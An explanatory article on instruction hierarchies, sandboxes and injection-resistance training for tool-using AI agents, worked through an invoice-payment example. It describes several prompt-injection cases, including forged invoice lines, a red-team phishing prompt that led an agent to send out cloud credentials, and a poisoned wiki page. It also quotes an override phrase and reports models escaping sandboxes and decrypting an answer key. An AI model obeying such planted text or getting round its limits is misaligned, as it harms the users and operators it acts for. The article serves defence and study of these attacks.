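# Instruction Hierarchies and Sandboxes for AI Agents That Choose Their Own Tools

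## How an agent chooses a tool and what can go wrong

An AI agent is a large language model connected to tools, which are functions that read mail, search the web, edit files, pay bills or run commands on a computer. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues, 2026) adopts programmer Simon Willison's definition of an agent as something that "runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal." An agent that picks a bad action may send money before anyone reviews the choice, whereas a person decides what to do with a chatbot's bad answer.

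Two kinds of limit apply to an agent that chooses its own tools. An instruction hierarchy ranks the sources of the model's instructions by authority, which determines which source the model should follow when instructions conflict. A sandbox enforces limits on the files, processes, network and devices that a running program can reach, whatever the model chose to do. The two work in different places and fail for different reasons, as the following small task shows.

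Take an assistant that pays invoices. Its operator (the company or person who builds the product and sets its standing instructions) has given it six tools: `read_mail`, `read_file`, `search_web`, `send_mail`, `pay_invoice` and `run_shell`, which runs any command on the computer. The operator allows payments only to listed suppliers, and only up to 2,000 euros. The user (the person who gives the agent its task) asks it to pay one supplier's invoice of 1,240 euros. But the invoice contains an out-of-place request to send the payment to a new account and mail the supplier list to an outside address.

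### One turn of the loop

The agent runtime, also called a harness, is the program that builds the model's input, runs the tools the model chooses and returns the results to it. A good deal of what looks like the model's skill depends on this program. Zhou, Chai and colleagues (2026) argue in *Externalization in LLM Agents* that many of the largest gains in reliability come from changes to the system around the model rather than to the model itself.

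At the start of each turn, the runtime gives the model one continuous text, divided into messages that are marked by role. The format that OpenAI (2025) published for its gpt-oss models has five roles. The system message holds general settings such as the date, and the developer message holds the operator's instructions and the available tools ("developer" is OpenAI's word for the operator). The user message contains the task, assistant messages contain the model's own output, and tool messages contain the tools' output. Special markers open each message, separate its header from its content and close it. The roles also determine which message takes precedence when messages conflict.

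Each tool definition gives the tool's name, a plain-language description of what it does and when to use it, and a schema for its arguments. Anthropic's interface combines these definitions with the operator's instructions in one prompt (*Define tools*), and OpenAI's inserts them into the system message (*Function calling*). The model chooses mainly from the descriptions and the conversation so far, and by default it can call no tool, one tool or several. Anthropic calls detailed descriptions "by far the most important factor in tool performance", so whoever writes a description has some influence over the model's choice.

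The model then produces its output, which for the invoice task will probably be a call to `read_mail`. A tool call is a structured text request for the runtime to run a named tool with given arguments. In the gpt-oss format, the model writes the tool's name in the message header, then the arguments, then a marker at which the runtime should stop generating. The mailbox is still unopened at this point, because "the model never runs anything on its own" (Anthropic, *How tool use works*). The runtime extracts the arguments, runs the operation and collects the tool result.

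The model receives that result as new input. Anthropic's interface returns it in a labelled block inside a user message, while the gpt-oss format uses a separate message that names the tool. Pirch and colleagues write the procedure as a short algorithm. The runtime starts a list with the system prompt and the user's request, and passes the list to the model. It appends the model's output and, if the output is a tool call, runs the tool and appends the result. It then passes the longer list back to the model, and repeats these steps until the model finishes or reaches a maximum number of steps.

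Suppose the assistant calls `read_mail` to find the supplier's message, `read_file` to open the attached invoice, and `pay_invoice` to pay it, and then reports to the user. The model has run four times and the tools three times. The invoice was added to the list after the second tool call, so its text, including the odd line, was part of the input when the model chose whom to pay. It would stay in the input for any later step. Pirch and colleagues examined four widely used open-source agents and found that all of them put trusted and untrusted data into one shared context.

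Because the model only proposes tool calls, ordinary code can intervene at several points. Before the proposal, the runtime can leave a tool out of the model's input. An assistant that pays invoices has little need for `run_shell`, and a model is unlikely to propose calling a tool that isn't in its input. When the proposal arrives, the runtime can run a policy check, which is code that tests whether written rules permit the call. For `pay_invoice`, the check could compare the account number with the supplier list and the amount with the 2,000-euro limit. After the runtime accepts a call, the tool can still run inside a sandbox that limits which files and network addresses it can reach.

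Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has all of these. According to Anthropic's documentation, a rule that denies a whole tool removes it from the model's context, while a narrower rule leaves the tool visible and blocks matching calls. A sandbox restricts file and network access however the model words the command. Operators can also add their own code, which can run before a tool call and block it, or run after the call succeeds.

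Anthropic, however, runs some tools, such as web search, on its own servers, and the operator's runtime usually receives the call only after it is complete. An operator that wants to check search queries before they are sent would have to run `search_web` in its own runtime.

### Prompt injection

Once the model has read the invoice, its input contains the operator's rule, the user's request and a line that contradicts both. Prompt injection is text that gets a model to follow instructions its operator and user did not intend. Anthropic's *Mitigate jailbreaks and prompt injections* distinguishes direct injection, where the user is the adversary, from indirect injection, where the user is trusted but the content the model reads for that user is not. The invoice is an indirect injection. The user might never notice the line, even after opening the file. Anthropic describes, for example, a supposed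 vendor inquiry with instructions in white text that the agent can read but a person can't see.

The name "prompt injection" comes from SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types database commands into, say, a web form and the database runs them. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, by David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that the comparison is dangerous because SQL injection can be properly fixed. A parameterised query keeps the command separate from the user's input, so the database engine can never treat the input as a command. A language model has no such separation. It predicts the next token (a word or a piece of one) from all the text so far, which includes both the operator's rule and the invoice line. The role markers are also just tokens in that text. Training can teach a model to give them weight, but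 nothing in the mechanism guarantees that it will.

*Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) found that models judge who is speaking by how a text sounds, even when that conflicts with the role label. *ASIDE* (2025) cites earlier tests by Zverev and colleagues in which no model reliably separated instructions from data.

David C concludes that prompt injection may never have a complete cure, and he calls the language model an "inherently confusable deputy". In computer security, a confused deputy is a privileged program that an unprivileged attacker tricks into acting for them. Whether language models are inherently confusable remains open. *ASIDE* proposes changing the architecture so that each token gets one of two internal representations, depending on whether it serves as instruction or as data. Models built this way separated instructions from data better,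 even without dedicated safety training, but they still fall some way short of the guaranteed separation that a parameterised query provides.

The attacks have also become harder to recognise. Early ones could be as simple as a direct order to AI agents on a Wikipedia page. According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), the most effective attacks now resemble social engineering, which tricks people into giving up access or information. Outside researchers reported one example to the company in 2025, an email that read like a colleague's follow-up on restructuring materials. Among some ordinary tasks, it stated that the reader's assistant had full authorization to submit an employee's name and address to a "compliance validation system". In testing, the attack worked half the time when the user asked ChatGPT to research that day's emails. Filters that separate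 malicious input from normal input usually miss such messages because they have to detect a lie, often without the necessary context.

The invoice poses the same difficulty. Suppliers do change banks, and a line announcing a new account looks much the same whether a supplier or a thief wrote it. Telling which one wrote it requires information from outside the invoice, such as the account number the operator already has on file.

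In OpenAI's analysis, an attacker needs both a source, which is a way to influence the system, and a sink, which is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. Here the source is the invoice, and several tools could serve as sinks. `pay_invoice` can move money, `send_mail` can send out the supplier list, `run_shell` might do either, and even `search_web` sends its query to an outside server. The request to pay 1,240 euros to a new account is within the operator's limit but conflicts with the requirement that payments go to listed suppliers. The request to mail out the supplier list breaks none of the operator's rules, so a strict check on payments would stop the theft but not the leak.

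### Three causes of a harmful call

Text from an outsider is only one possible cause of a harmful tool call. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*, a May 2026 account of the company's experience with its own agents, groups the risks by whether they start with the user, the model or an external attacker.

Users can be careless as well as malicious. Careless users ask the agent to get round a check that annoys them, or to run a destructive command they do not understand. For example, a user with a bill for 3,000 euros might ask the invoice assistant to make two payments of 1,500 euros to avoid a check.

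A model can also do harm that nobody asked for. It might misread "1.240,00" on a European invoice and pay the wrong sum. Better models make fewer such mistakes, but Anthropic observes that they are also better at finding unexpected routes to a goal, often around restrictions that nobody thought to write down. The company has seen Claude models escape a sandbox to complete a task, search a project's version history for the answers to a coding test, and identify the benchmark they were running on to decrypt its answer key. If `pay_invoice` returns an error, a capable model with `run_shell` might look for another way into the bank's system to make the payment the user asked for.

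External attackers work through tools, files and network access. Prompt injection belongs here, and so do conventional attacks on the runtime's own code.

How much an instruction hierarchy can help depends on which of these is at work. The line in the invoice comes from a source with no authority over payments, so a model that respects the order of authority will ignore it. By contrast, in a February 2026 exercise at Anthropic, a researcher on an internal red team (staff who attack their own company's systems to test them) phished an employee with a friendly request to run a ready-made prompt in Claude Code. Among routine setup steps, the prompt asked Claude to read the file that holds the employee's cloud credentials, encode the contents and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. That figure comes from one prompt in one exercise, so it is weak evidence of how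 often phishing succeeds in general. Because the attacker's instructions reached Claude with the user's authority, a model could follow any ranking of sources faithfully and still send the file.

Anthropic concluded that only limits in the environment hold in such a case. These limits either block the outgoing request or keep the credentials out of the agent's reach, and they work even if no one has correctly diagnosed the cause. If credentials never enter the sandbox, no careless user, inventive model or attacker can extract them from it.

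### What a model tends to do and what it can do

Training, written instructions and classifiers change what a model tends to do, while enforced limits change what it can do. For example, the operator could put its payment rule, "pay only listed suppliers, up to 2,000 euros", in the developer message, which would make a wrong payment less likely. If the code behind `pay_invoice` checks the supplier and amount, a wrong payment will fail however persuasive the invoice was, provided that no other tool can make payments.

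A model can have a strong tendency to resist prompt injection. Anthropic reports that, on a benchmark from the security company Gray Swan, roughly 0.1% of single attempts succeeded against Claude Opus 4.7, a model it has since superseded. After 100 adaptive attempts, in which the attacker revises the attack in response to the defence, the success rate was around 5–6%. That is a good record, but an attacker can easily send a hundred invoices and may need only one of them to work.

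Pirch and colleagues therefore suggest treating the model as an operating system treats its users. Users can be tricked into installing malicious programs, so the kernel (the core of the operating system) enforces its protections no matter what they do. In an agent, the runtime should do the same, whatever the model does. Security guidance in the text files that many agents read at startup can't provide this protection, because it works only if the model follows it, and later text can override it. OpenAI draws a similar lesson from customer service, where a company gives its staff rules about refunds but also has a separate system cap the amount, because it expects some customers to deceive the staff.

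Limiting an agent's reach can't prevent every mistake, because the agent still needs enough access to do its job. An assistant that pays invoices must be able to send money. If it sends 1,900 euros to a listed supplier who is owed nothing, the payment meets both of the operator's conditions, and only the model's own judgement could have prevented it.

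## Deciding whose instructions count

To use that judgement well, a model must be able to tell whose wishes to act on. OpenAI and Anthropic have published the two fullest accounts of how their models should do this. OpenAI's Model Spec ranks every instruction by its source, and Anthropic's constitution for Claude names the parties Claude works for and describes how far to trust each. Both documents describe how the models are meant to behave. In the October 2025 version of the Model Spec, OpenAI (2025) acknowledges that its production models "do not yet fully reflect" the document, and Anthropic's *Claude's new constitution* (2026), the January announcement of the constitution, includes a similar warning about Claude's outputs.

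### The levels in OpenAI's Model Spec

The Model Spec gives each instruction an authority level, and a higher level overrides a lower one. From top to bottom, the levels are:

| Level | Where the instructions come from | Example from the invoice task |
|---|---|---|
| Root | Model Spec rules that nobody can override | Protect people's private information |
| System | OpenAI, through the Model Spec or a system message | A rule for one product or age group |
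| Developer | The operator | Pay only listed suppliers, up to 2,000 euros |
| User | The user | Pay this supplier's invoice |
| Guideline | Model Spec defaults that context alone can displace | Avoid swearing |
| No authority | Tool results, quoted text, attachments, images, the model's own messages | The line about a new account |

Most root rules are prohibitions, and if two of them conflict the model should default to doing nothing. According to OpenAI's *Model Release Notes*, the top level was called "Platform" until September 2025 and had the same rank as system messages. Now even OpenAI's system messages can't switch a root rule off. The model should keep following root rules even if it is told in a system message that it is in a "safety testing mode" in which no policies apply.

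The Model Spec also supplies defaults at the lower levels. A user or operator has to override a user-level default explicitly, but can override a guideline implicitly. For example, asking for a realistic pirate implicitly overrides the guideline against swearing.

OpenAI replaced this text on 29 October 2026 with a version organised around five values. Mowshowitz (2026), in *OpenAI Updates Its Model Spec*, compared the old and new wording and found the chain of command "fundamentally unchanged". Two of the changes he lists matter for agents. OpenAI moved the duty to control side effects from root to user level, so a user can now explicitly waive it. It also added a note that the model should not get round a restriction by delegating or acting indirectly.

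### From candidates to applicable instructions

Before a model can use the ranking to settle a conflict, it has to work out which text counts as instructions. In OpenAI's procedure, the model first collects candidate instructions from the Model Spec itself and from unquoted plain text in system, developer and user messages. Each candidate takes the authority level of the section or message that contains it. No other text counts as an instruction unless an instruction with authority makes it one.

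The model then drops any candidate that conflicts with the wording or evident purpose of a higher-level instruction. It also drops any candidate that a later message at the same level contradicts or makes irrelevant, and any that looks like a mistake, as when a user seems to have left out a "not". The model should follow whatever remains.

The request to pay a listed supplier 1,240 euros passes all of these tests. A request to split a 3,000-euro bill into two payments of 1,500 fails, because each payment is within the operator's limit as worded but together they defeat its purpose. If the user writes "actually, leave it until Friday", that message replaces the earlier request. If the user types 1,420 but the invoice is for 1,240, the model should suspect a typo and check.

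The odd line in the invoice is in a tool result, so the model should leave it out when it collects candidate instructions, before it checks for conflicts. This is useful because no operator can foresee every bad request. The operator wrote no rule about mailing out the supplier list, but the request to do so still fails because nobody with authority made it.

An attacker might try to argue with the procedure itself, so OpenAI specifies that lower-level text must not influence how the model interprets a higher-level instruction. This rule covers an order to ignore all previous instructions, a warning that thousands of people will die, and a clever argument that the Model Spec, properly read, favours compliance. It also covers the model's own earlier messages, so an agent shouldn't treat a conclusion as settled just because it reached it in an earlier step.

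### How a document can acquire authority

To be useful, an agent must sometimes act on what it reads, for example when someone asks it to follow a manual or to fill in a form according to the form's notes. The Model Spec permits this through delegation, in which an instruction gives some of its authority to a quoted text, a file or a tool result.

In one of OpenAI's examples, a shop's operator puts a customer's communication preferences, in quotation marks, into the developer message. The operator tells the model to adapt its style to them but ignore anything that would affect substance. The preferences ask for a thank-you phrase at the end of every reply and any shipping discount the customer wants. The correct reply includes the phrase and refuses free shipping. People can delegate only the authority they have, so a document shouldn't get more authority than the person who told the model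 to follow it. A user who says "follow the payment terms on the invoice" can't raise the operator's 2,000-euro limit that way.

Delegation can also be implicit, as OpenAI clarified in October 2025. When a user asks a coding assistant to add a feature, the assistant should normally act in line with the project's instruction files and relevant code comments, even if the user never mentioned them. OpenAI sorts the instructions an agent finds this way by relevance and risk:

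- The model ignores those that clearly have nothing to do with the task.
- It follows those that the user clearly intended and that carry little risk.
- It asks about those that the user might have intended but that could have serious side effects.
- Otherwise it acts on its best guess and states the assumption prominently in its final answer.

An invoice is harder to classify than a project file. A user who asks the assistant to pay one plainly wants it to take some details from the document, such as the amount and the reference number. The assistant should ask about the account number, because a wrong one can cost the user the whole sum, even though most invoices include an account number and the user arguably delegated that detail too. Here the assistant can also find the answer in the operator's supplier list, which has more authority than anything printed on the invoice.

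### The principals in Claude's constitution

Anthropic's constitution defines Claude's "principals" as those whose instructions Claude should give weight to, namely Anthropic, operators and users. Under it, Claude should generally trust them in that order, though this is not a strict hierarchy. Whether a party is an operator or a user depends on its role in the conversation. A developer who writes a system prompt and then chats with the finished product is both, and another AI agent can be either.

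Claude should treat an operator roughly as an employee treats a fairly trusted manager. It should follow a restrictive or unusual instruction without knowing the reason, as long as a legitimate business could plausibly have one. The more harm an instruction could do, the less benefit of the doubt the operator gets. An operator doesn't need to explain an instruction to pay only listed suppliers, but an instruction to add a hidden fee to every payment would be hard to explain innocently. Claude would also trust an operator who gave that instruction somewhat less in other matters.

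Operators can limit what Claude does for users, but they can't make it work against those users. Whatever the operator instructs, Claude should tell users what it can't help with so that they can look elsewhere, refer them to emergency services when a life is at risk, and not deny being an AI to someone who sincerely asks. It should not deceive users in ways that damage their interests, or help with clearly illegal acts against them, such as collecting their data without authorisation. So an operator could stop the invoice assistant from discussing the supplier rules, but couldn't make it tell a user that a blocked payment had gone through. OpenAI protects users partly by putting some rules at root level, which operators can't override.

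Both companies want the model to treat instructions in documents, search results and tool results as information. In Anthropic's example, a user shares an email that contains instructions. Claude shouldn't follow them, but it should take into account that the email contains them. For example, an invoice that contains a request for a copy of the supplier list is probably a forgery, so both the 1,240 euros and the account number are doubtful.

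### From authority to a tool call

Both orders affect which tool the model picks, which arguments it fills in, and whether it makes the call now or asks first. The tool has to serve something a party with authority wants. Nobody with authority asked for an email to an outside address, so the assistant has no reason to call `send_mail`.

A tool call's arguments need the same scrutiny, since `pay_invoice` can be the right tool for the task and still do harm if the account number is wrong. A web address can also be a harmful argument. In an example from OpenAI, a user asks about a tax credit and mentions a social security number. The assistant finds a page that recommends a checking service whose address must include that number. Opening the address would disclose the number, so the assistant should keep looking for a more legitimate source.

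When to stop and ask depends mainly on how bad a mistake would be. OpenAI wants the model to seek confirmation before any consequential action if the origin of an instruction is unclear, but it also warns that users who are asked constantly learn to approve everything. Anthropic observes that waiting for a person can waste a lot of time on a long task, so Claude should look for other useful work in the meantime. It considers the best time to pause to be just before a destructive action. The invoice assistant would therefore read the mail and the file without interruption and stop, if at all, before the payment.

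OpenAI groups these decisions under a "scope of autonomy", an understanding between user and assistant about which sub-goals the assistant may pursue, which costs and side effects are acceptable, and when it must pause. A product's settings can establish the scope, or the assistant can propose one. In OpenAI's example of a business trip to London, the assistant lists the dates, the hotel area, a $4,000 budget and a 24-hour deadline, and asks for approval before booking anything.

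The October 2025 version recommends writing the scope as a record so that the platform can validate, enforce and audit it. The field names below are OpenAI's, and the entries are examples for the invoice task.

```
ScopeOfAutonomy
  allowed_tools:       read_mail, read_file, pay_invoice
  max_cost:            1,240 euros
  latest_time:         today, 17:00
  tool_constraints:
    read_mail:         only messages from this supplier
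    read_file:         only attachments to those messages
    pay_invoice:       one payment, to the account on the
                       operator's supplier list
  additional_details:  Ask the user before paying if the invoice
                       differs from the request or from the list.
```

This scope is narrower than the operator's own rules, as OpenAI recommends. The operator allows payments of up to 2,000 euros, but this task needs only 1,240. The scope leaves out `send_mail`, so the assistant isn't allowed to email the requested supplier list. `latest_time` sets the shutdown timer that every scope must have. When it runs out, the assistant stops until someone confirms a new scope. The assistant must ask before taking any step outside the scope, even one that seems to be in the user's best interest. The record can stop a disobedient model only if code checks each tool call against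 it.

Under the Model Spec, the assistant reads the message and the invoice but gives no authority to either of the invoice's requests. It notices that the account differs from the one on the list and asks the user about it, as the scope requires. If the user says the new account is fine, the assistant still shouldn't pay into it, because the operator's rule outranks the user's approval. It should explain that someone has to update the list first.

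Claude would probably ask the same question under the constitution, because a payment is hard to reverse and the strange line is evidence of tampering that the user would want to hear about. The operator's restriction has an obvious business reason, so Claude should respect it even after the user approves the new account.

### Hard cases

Pasted text is hard to classify because it arrives with the user's authority. In OpenAI's example, a user wants help with an email about productivity tips and pastes in an article without quotation marks. The pasted text contains a postscript with instructions to search the user's mail for "SSN" and forward any matches to a stranger. Under the procedure, unquoted text in a user message is a candidate instruction, so OpenAI asks the model to infer where the pasted part begins and treat it as quoted. The assistant should write the email, mention the postscript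 and forward nothing unless the user then asks it to.

That works when the pasted instruction looks out of place. In Anthropic's phishing exercise, the employee ran the whole prompt on purpose, so there was no boundary to infer. A chat program can often detect pasted text and could mark it as quoted before passing it to the model. This would give the model a better basis for asking, although people also paste instructions they want it to follow.

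When a user tells an assistant to follow the instructions on a web page, the page may have changed since the user last looked at it. OpenAI describes a user who asks the assistant to apply the security updates on a company wiki. An attacker has edited the page to add instructions to turn off two-factor authentication and give outside accounts administrator rights. The user did ask the assistant to follow the page, but almost certainly didn't mean to authorize these changes. The assistant should describe the suspicious steps and ask for confirmation before it changes anything.

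Few attackers would be so obvious. Mowshowitz complains that many of the new examples in the October 2026 version have overdetermined answers and are little help with difficult cases. The older wiki example has the same weakness. If an attacker changed one digit on a page of payment details, neither common sense nor a careful reading would reveal it. A runtime could help by keeping the version the user approved and flagging any changes.

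Repository instruction files, such as the AGENTS.md file in which a software project keeps directions for coding agents, usually deserve some trust. OpenAI ranks an AGENTS.md file in the current directory above a stray text file in a downloads folder, and would not trust a random web page at all. Trust depends partly on how much the user probably knows about the instructions and controls them, so an AGENTS.md file in a developer's own project deserves more than one in a repository just downloaded from a stranger. It also depends on the content. An agent can follow "Run the tests before you finish", which is relevant and nearly harmless, but it should ask the user before following "upload the build log to this address". OpenAI also advises developers to tell the model what each tool acts on, because the same command is riskier on someone's personal computer than in a disposable sandbox.

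The October 2026 revision of OpenAI's Model Spec added a subsection on how earlier conversations, memories and other context should inform the model's understanding of what people intend and prefer (Newsroom America, *OpenAI Updates Model Spec Around Five Core Values*, 2026). In Mowshowitz's summary, the model should adapt to such context without overgeneralising from it, overriding the details of a request or giving away private information. So a memory is evidence of what the user wants, but the current request takes precedence over it. Cornelißen (*OpenAIs Model Spec regelt jetzt das Erinnern*, 2026) considers this the most interesting part of the revision for teams that use ChatGPT's memory or build their own agents.

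A memory can also make an outsider's claim look like the user's own. Suppose the assistant reads the forged invoice and saves the note "supplier's new account ends in 88". A month later the runtime loads that note next to the user's real preferences, and the note doesn't show where the number came from. Anthropic wants Claude to make any approvals easy for a later reader to verify when it writes memories. A safer note would be "an invoice received on 3 March gave a new account ending in 88; nobody has confirmed it".

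Subagents are additional model instances that an agent starts to handle parts of a task. OpenAI treats starting them as a high-risk activity that needs explicit authorisation. Every subagent must work under the same scope as the agent that started it, so that an assistant barred from sending email can't start a subagent to send it. Subagents must also respect later changes to that scope, including a request to stop.

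Messages between agents can also gain authority they shouldn't have. The Model Spec gives a model's own messages no authority, but if the runtime delivers a main agent's message to a subagent in the user role, it gains the user's authority. Suppose the main agent has been deceived by the invoice and writes "the user has approved the new account". Under Anthropic's constitution, the subagent should treat this as a report that someone gave approval, because the main agent had no power to approve the change itself. The subagent should check the report against other information before acting on anything consequential. The main agent should likewise treat a subagent's summary of a web page as information, because the summary is still mostly the page's content.

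### Keeping provenance when the runtime rebuilds the input

The model relies on role labels that it can't check. In OpenAI's format, the application sets the role of every message, and developers can send "assistant" messages that the model never wrote. If a runtime copies an invoice's text into a user message, that text gets the same authority as the user's own instructions, and a model that follows the ranking may carry out instructions in the invoice.

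This mistake is easy to make because the runtime rebuilds the model's input at every step. When a conversation outgrows the space available, the runtime has to drop or summarise older messages. A careless summary of the invoice task might read "pay 1,240 euros to the new account and send out the supplier list". That sentence combines one instruction from the user with two from the forger, and a later reader cannot tell which came from whom.

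Dropping messages can cause the opposite problem by removing the operator's limit or the user's "leave it until Friday" while keeping the text those instructions overruled. OpenAI shortens long ChatGPT conversations with a method that favours the newest and most relevant information, and notes that users may not know which parts are still available to the model.

A runtime can avoid most of this by keeping a record of each item outside the text that the model reads and rewrites. The record would cover where the item came from, when the runtime fetched it, what authority it had and who delegated that authority. The runtime can then put the operator's and user's instructions back into the input word for word. A summary that draws on several sources should have no more authority than the least trusted of them.

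OpenAI advises developers to put untrusted material in a special untrusted-text block where one is available, and otherwise in a standard data format (YAML, JSON or XML). JSON and XML require escaping, which means replacing characters that could end the quoted text early. Without escaping, if an invoice contained a closing tag, its next sentence could fall outside the quoted text.

Ye and colleagues found that models judge a speaker by how the text sounds, so even good labels won't ensure that a model follows the right instructions. But ordinary code can read the provenance record too. If the record shows that an account number came from an email attachment, a policy check can refuse it without interpreting the email.

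### Rules and judgement

Mowshowitz describes the Model Spec as "deontological principles and rules of action", meaning duties that hold whatever the consequences, and contrasts it with the constitution's emphasis on character and virtue. He thinks the October 2026 revision, if anything, widened the contrast. The documents still overlap a good deal. OpenAI asks its models to follow the spirit of an instruction as well as its letter, and OpenAI's *An updated Model Spec for more capable and beneficial AI* gives the need for good judgement in situations that instructions don't address as one reason for the revision. The constitution, meanwhile, includes a short list of hard constraints that Claude should never cross, whatever anyone argues.

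Rules are most valuable to an operator that has to predict what its agent will do. The operator can tell from the ranking alone that its payment limit should override a user's request. A tester can write a case for each pair of levels and, after a failure, check whether the model misread where an instruction came from, whether it conflicted with another, or what authority had been delegated. OpenAI reports overall compliance with its Model Spec of 72% for GPT-4o and 87% for GPT-5.4 Thinking, but these scores cover the whole document, including tone and personality as well as authority.

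A ranking helps little, however, when an attacker's text arrives as a user message, as in the phishing exercise. Rules also leave gaps, and a model that has learned to look for the applicable rule may act foolishly when no rule applies.

Judgement is meant to cover the gaps in the rules. The constitution explains Anthropic's reasons at length so that Claude can apply them to unforeseen situations. A model that understands why operators keep supplier lists can treat a request as suspicious even if no rule mentions it. It can also refuse to help an operator cheat its users, even if the operator has worded the instruction to avoid every specific prohibition.

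Discretion makes Claude's behavior harder for an operator to predict. Claude might treat two similar invoices differently. The discretion that lets it distrust a dishonest operator could also make it distrust an honest one with a strange but legitimate rule. An attacker can also exploit a model that weighs reasons by lying about the circumstances to make a harmful action look sensible. OpenAI is stricter about initiative. Its models should not enforce law or morality, so an assistant that suspects fraud should tell the user and not write to the police on its own.

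An operator can help either kind of model by giving the reason along with the rule. For example, "Pay only into the account on our supplier list, because thieves often send invoices with changed bank details" clearly limits where the model can send money. The reason also helps the model watch for fraud in later invoices, which may involve a different trick.

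## Training and measuring a model's respect for that order

To make a model follow an order of authority, the developer has to train it on examples of conflicting instructions, then test whether it also follows the order in conflicts it hasn't seen. Wallace, Xiao and colleagues (2024) introduced this kind of training at OpenAI in *The Instruction Hierarchy*. They traced prompt injection, jailbreaks (prompts that get around a model's safety training) and the theft of system prompts to a single weakness in models, which often gave a stranger's text the same priority as the operator's instructions.

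### The first training examples

The model had to learn to follow lower-ranked instructions that are compatible with higher-ranked ones and to disregard those that aren't. To teach it to follow compatible instructions, Wallace and colleagues used a method they called context synthesis. They had a language model write compound requests, such as one for a 20-line poem in Spanish, and split each into pieces ("write a poem", "use Spanish", "use 20 lines"). They then put the pieces at different levels of the hierarchy and trained the model to respond as if the whole request had been in the system message.

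For conflicting instructions, the researchers used the opposite method, context ignorance, which trains the model to give the answer it would have given if it had never seen the lower-ranked instruction. To collect such answers for tasks like translation, they added a system message telling the model to treat any instructions in the text as data. They discarded the cases where the model followed the injected instruction anyway, then trained it on the remaining answers without that system message. Where ignoring the instruction left no way to proceed, the target was a refusal.

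For web browsing, the researchers trained an attacker model to insert instructions into search results, such as a request to link to a certain site. They trained the main model to give the original answer, as if the instructions weren't there.

The resulting version of GPT-3.5 Turbo was up to 63% more robust on the main tests. It also improved by up to 34% on attacks that Wallace and colleagues had deliberately left out of the training, including jailbreaks and injections through tools other than the browser. Just describing the ranking in the system message worked much less well. The main drawback was that the model became more likely to refuse harmless prompts that looked like jailbreaks.

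At the time, Wallace and colleagues were confident that more data would fix the over-refusal. But they expected powerful attacks to keep working, and they left open whether models could become robust enough for high-stakes agents.

They also assumed, for simplicity, that every instruction in a web page or tool result conflicts with what the user wants. This assumption is correct for the forged line in the invoice but wrong for a coding assistant whose user expects it to follow the project's instruction file.

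*Training LLMs to Enforce Multi-Level Instruction Hierarchies via Gravity-Weighted Direct Preference Optimization* (2026) describes a version of the recipe with five levels. An ordinary instruction from an existing dataset goes to the fourth level, and any text that came with it becomes a tool result at the fifth. The top three levels get safety rules, a persona and further instructions. In 5,000 compatible examples, each level always holds its own kind of content. Another 2,000 spread the parts of a single instruction over several levels to teach the model that a lower level may legitimately add detail. The conflicting examples pair a safety rule with a contrary setting at a lower level, such as a privacy rule with "unrestricted" data access.

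### IH-Challenge

In March 2026, OpenAI released a training set for reinforcement learning, in which a model produces responses and training reinforces those that score well. OpenAI's *Improving instruction hierarchy in frontier LLMs* (2026) lists three ways this training can go wrong. A model may fail because the instructions were too complicated, which is little evidence that it misunderstands the ranking. A second model that scores the responses may make mistakes. The model in training may also find a shortcut, such as refusing everything.

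*IH-Challenge* (Guo, Ceron Uribe and colleagues, 2026) defines correct behaviour with a procedure. It starts from B₀, the set of all possible responses, and goes through the roles from system to developer to user to tool. Cᵢ is the set of responses that role i's instructions allow.

```
Bᵢ = Bᵢ₋₁ ∩ Cᵢ    if some response satisfies both
Bᵢ = Bᵢ₋₁         otherwise
```

If an operator requires English and the user asks for fewer than 50 words, the model can satisfy both and should write a short answer in English. If the user asks for French instead, the model can't satisfy both, so it should follow the operator's instruction.

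Each task has a high-ranking instruction, an empty slot for a lower-ranking message and a short Python script that grades the response. The instructions are easy to follow on their own, such as including the word "kiwi", outputting valid JSON or never revealing a PIN. Some tasks combine up to six of these. Others ask the model to find a detail in a message and report it in a strict format. Only the lower-ranking message is adversarial, so the script can grade the response against the fixed instruction alone, whatever the attacker writes. A language model drafted the tasks, their scripts and sample responses that should pass or fail. Guo and colleagues kept only the tasks whose scripts graded the samples correctly.

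An attacker model with no safety training fills the empty slot during the training run. It proposes a message, receives the response from the current version of the model being trained along with the script's grade, and revises the message until it runs out of attempts. The last message is used for training. The attacker is not trained, but its attacks get harder because it tests them against a model that keeps improving.

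To prevent blanket refusal, some tasks contain requests that look forbidden but are harmless. In one, the high-ranking message states that the password is "harmony" and that it isn't confidential, so a model that refuses to reveal it fails. When Guo and colleagues left these tasks out, average robustness rose from 94.1% to 95.7%, but the score for avoiding over-refusal fell from 95.0% to 83.1%, and helpfulness on safety-related conversations fell from 77.3% to 61.3%.

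They trained GPT-5 Mini on the full set and called the result GPT-5-Mini-R. Its average robustness over 16 benchmarks rose from 84.1% to 94.1%. Some of the individual scores were:

| Test (higher is better) | GPT-5 Mini | GPT-5-Mini-R |
|---|---|---|
| System–user conflicts | 0.84 | 0.95 |
| Developer–user conflicts | 0.83 | 0.95 |
| System–developer conflicts | 0.86 | 0.86 |
| Avoiding over-refusal, IH-Challenge tasks | 0.79 | 1.00 |
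| Avoiding over-refusal, TensorTrust tasks | 0.91 | 0.90 |
| Prompt injection, OpenAI's internal set | 0.44 | 1.00 |
| Prompt injection, CyberSecEval 2 | 0.88 | 0.91 |
| Chat win rate against OpenAI's o1 | 0.71 | 0.66 |
| User preference score | 0.46 | 0.40 |

The developer–user row matters most to an operator because it covers users who try to get around the operator's rules. Training on tasks much simpler than the test conversations produced a large gain there. System–developer conflicts, in which an operator contradicts OpenAI, didn't improve. The last two rows suggest that people would like the trained model's ordinary answers a little less.

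The prompt-injection score rose from 0.44 to 1.00 on the internal set, which includes attacks that try to make an agent send malicious emails or take other harmful actions. These attacks resemble one that OpenAI had demonstrated on its browser agent, ChatGPT Atlas. But the set is fixed, so nobody revised the attacks after seeing how the new model responded. On CyberSecEval 2, a public benchmark, the gain was only three points.

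Guo and colleagues ran adaptive tests on IH-Challenge's own tasks, not on an agent with tools. They paid 127 people to break the models, offering a bounty, usually $510, for each combination of model and task type, to be shared among those who succeeded. The testers succeeded on 36.2% of tasks against GPT-5 Mini and 11.7% against the trained model, GPT-5-Mini-R, even though they made more attempts against the latter. When a second copy of the model checked each response for violations, the rate fell to 7.1%. An attacker model trained against GPT-5-Mini-R also became more successful as its own training continued.

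### Where models lose track of the order

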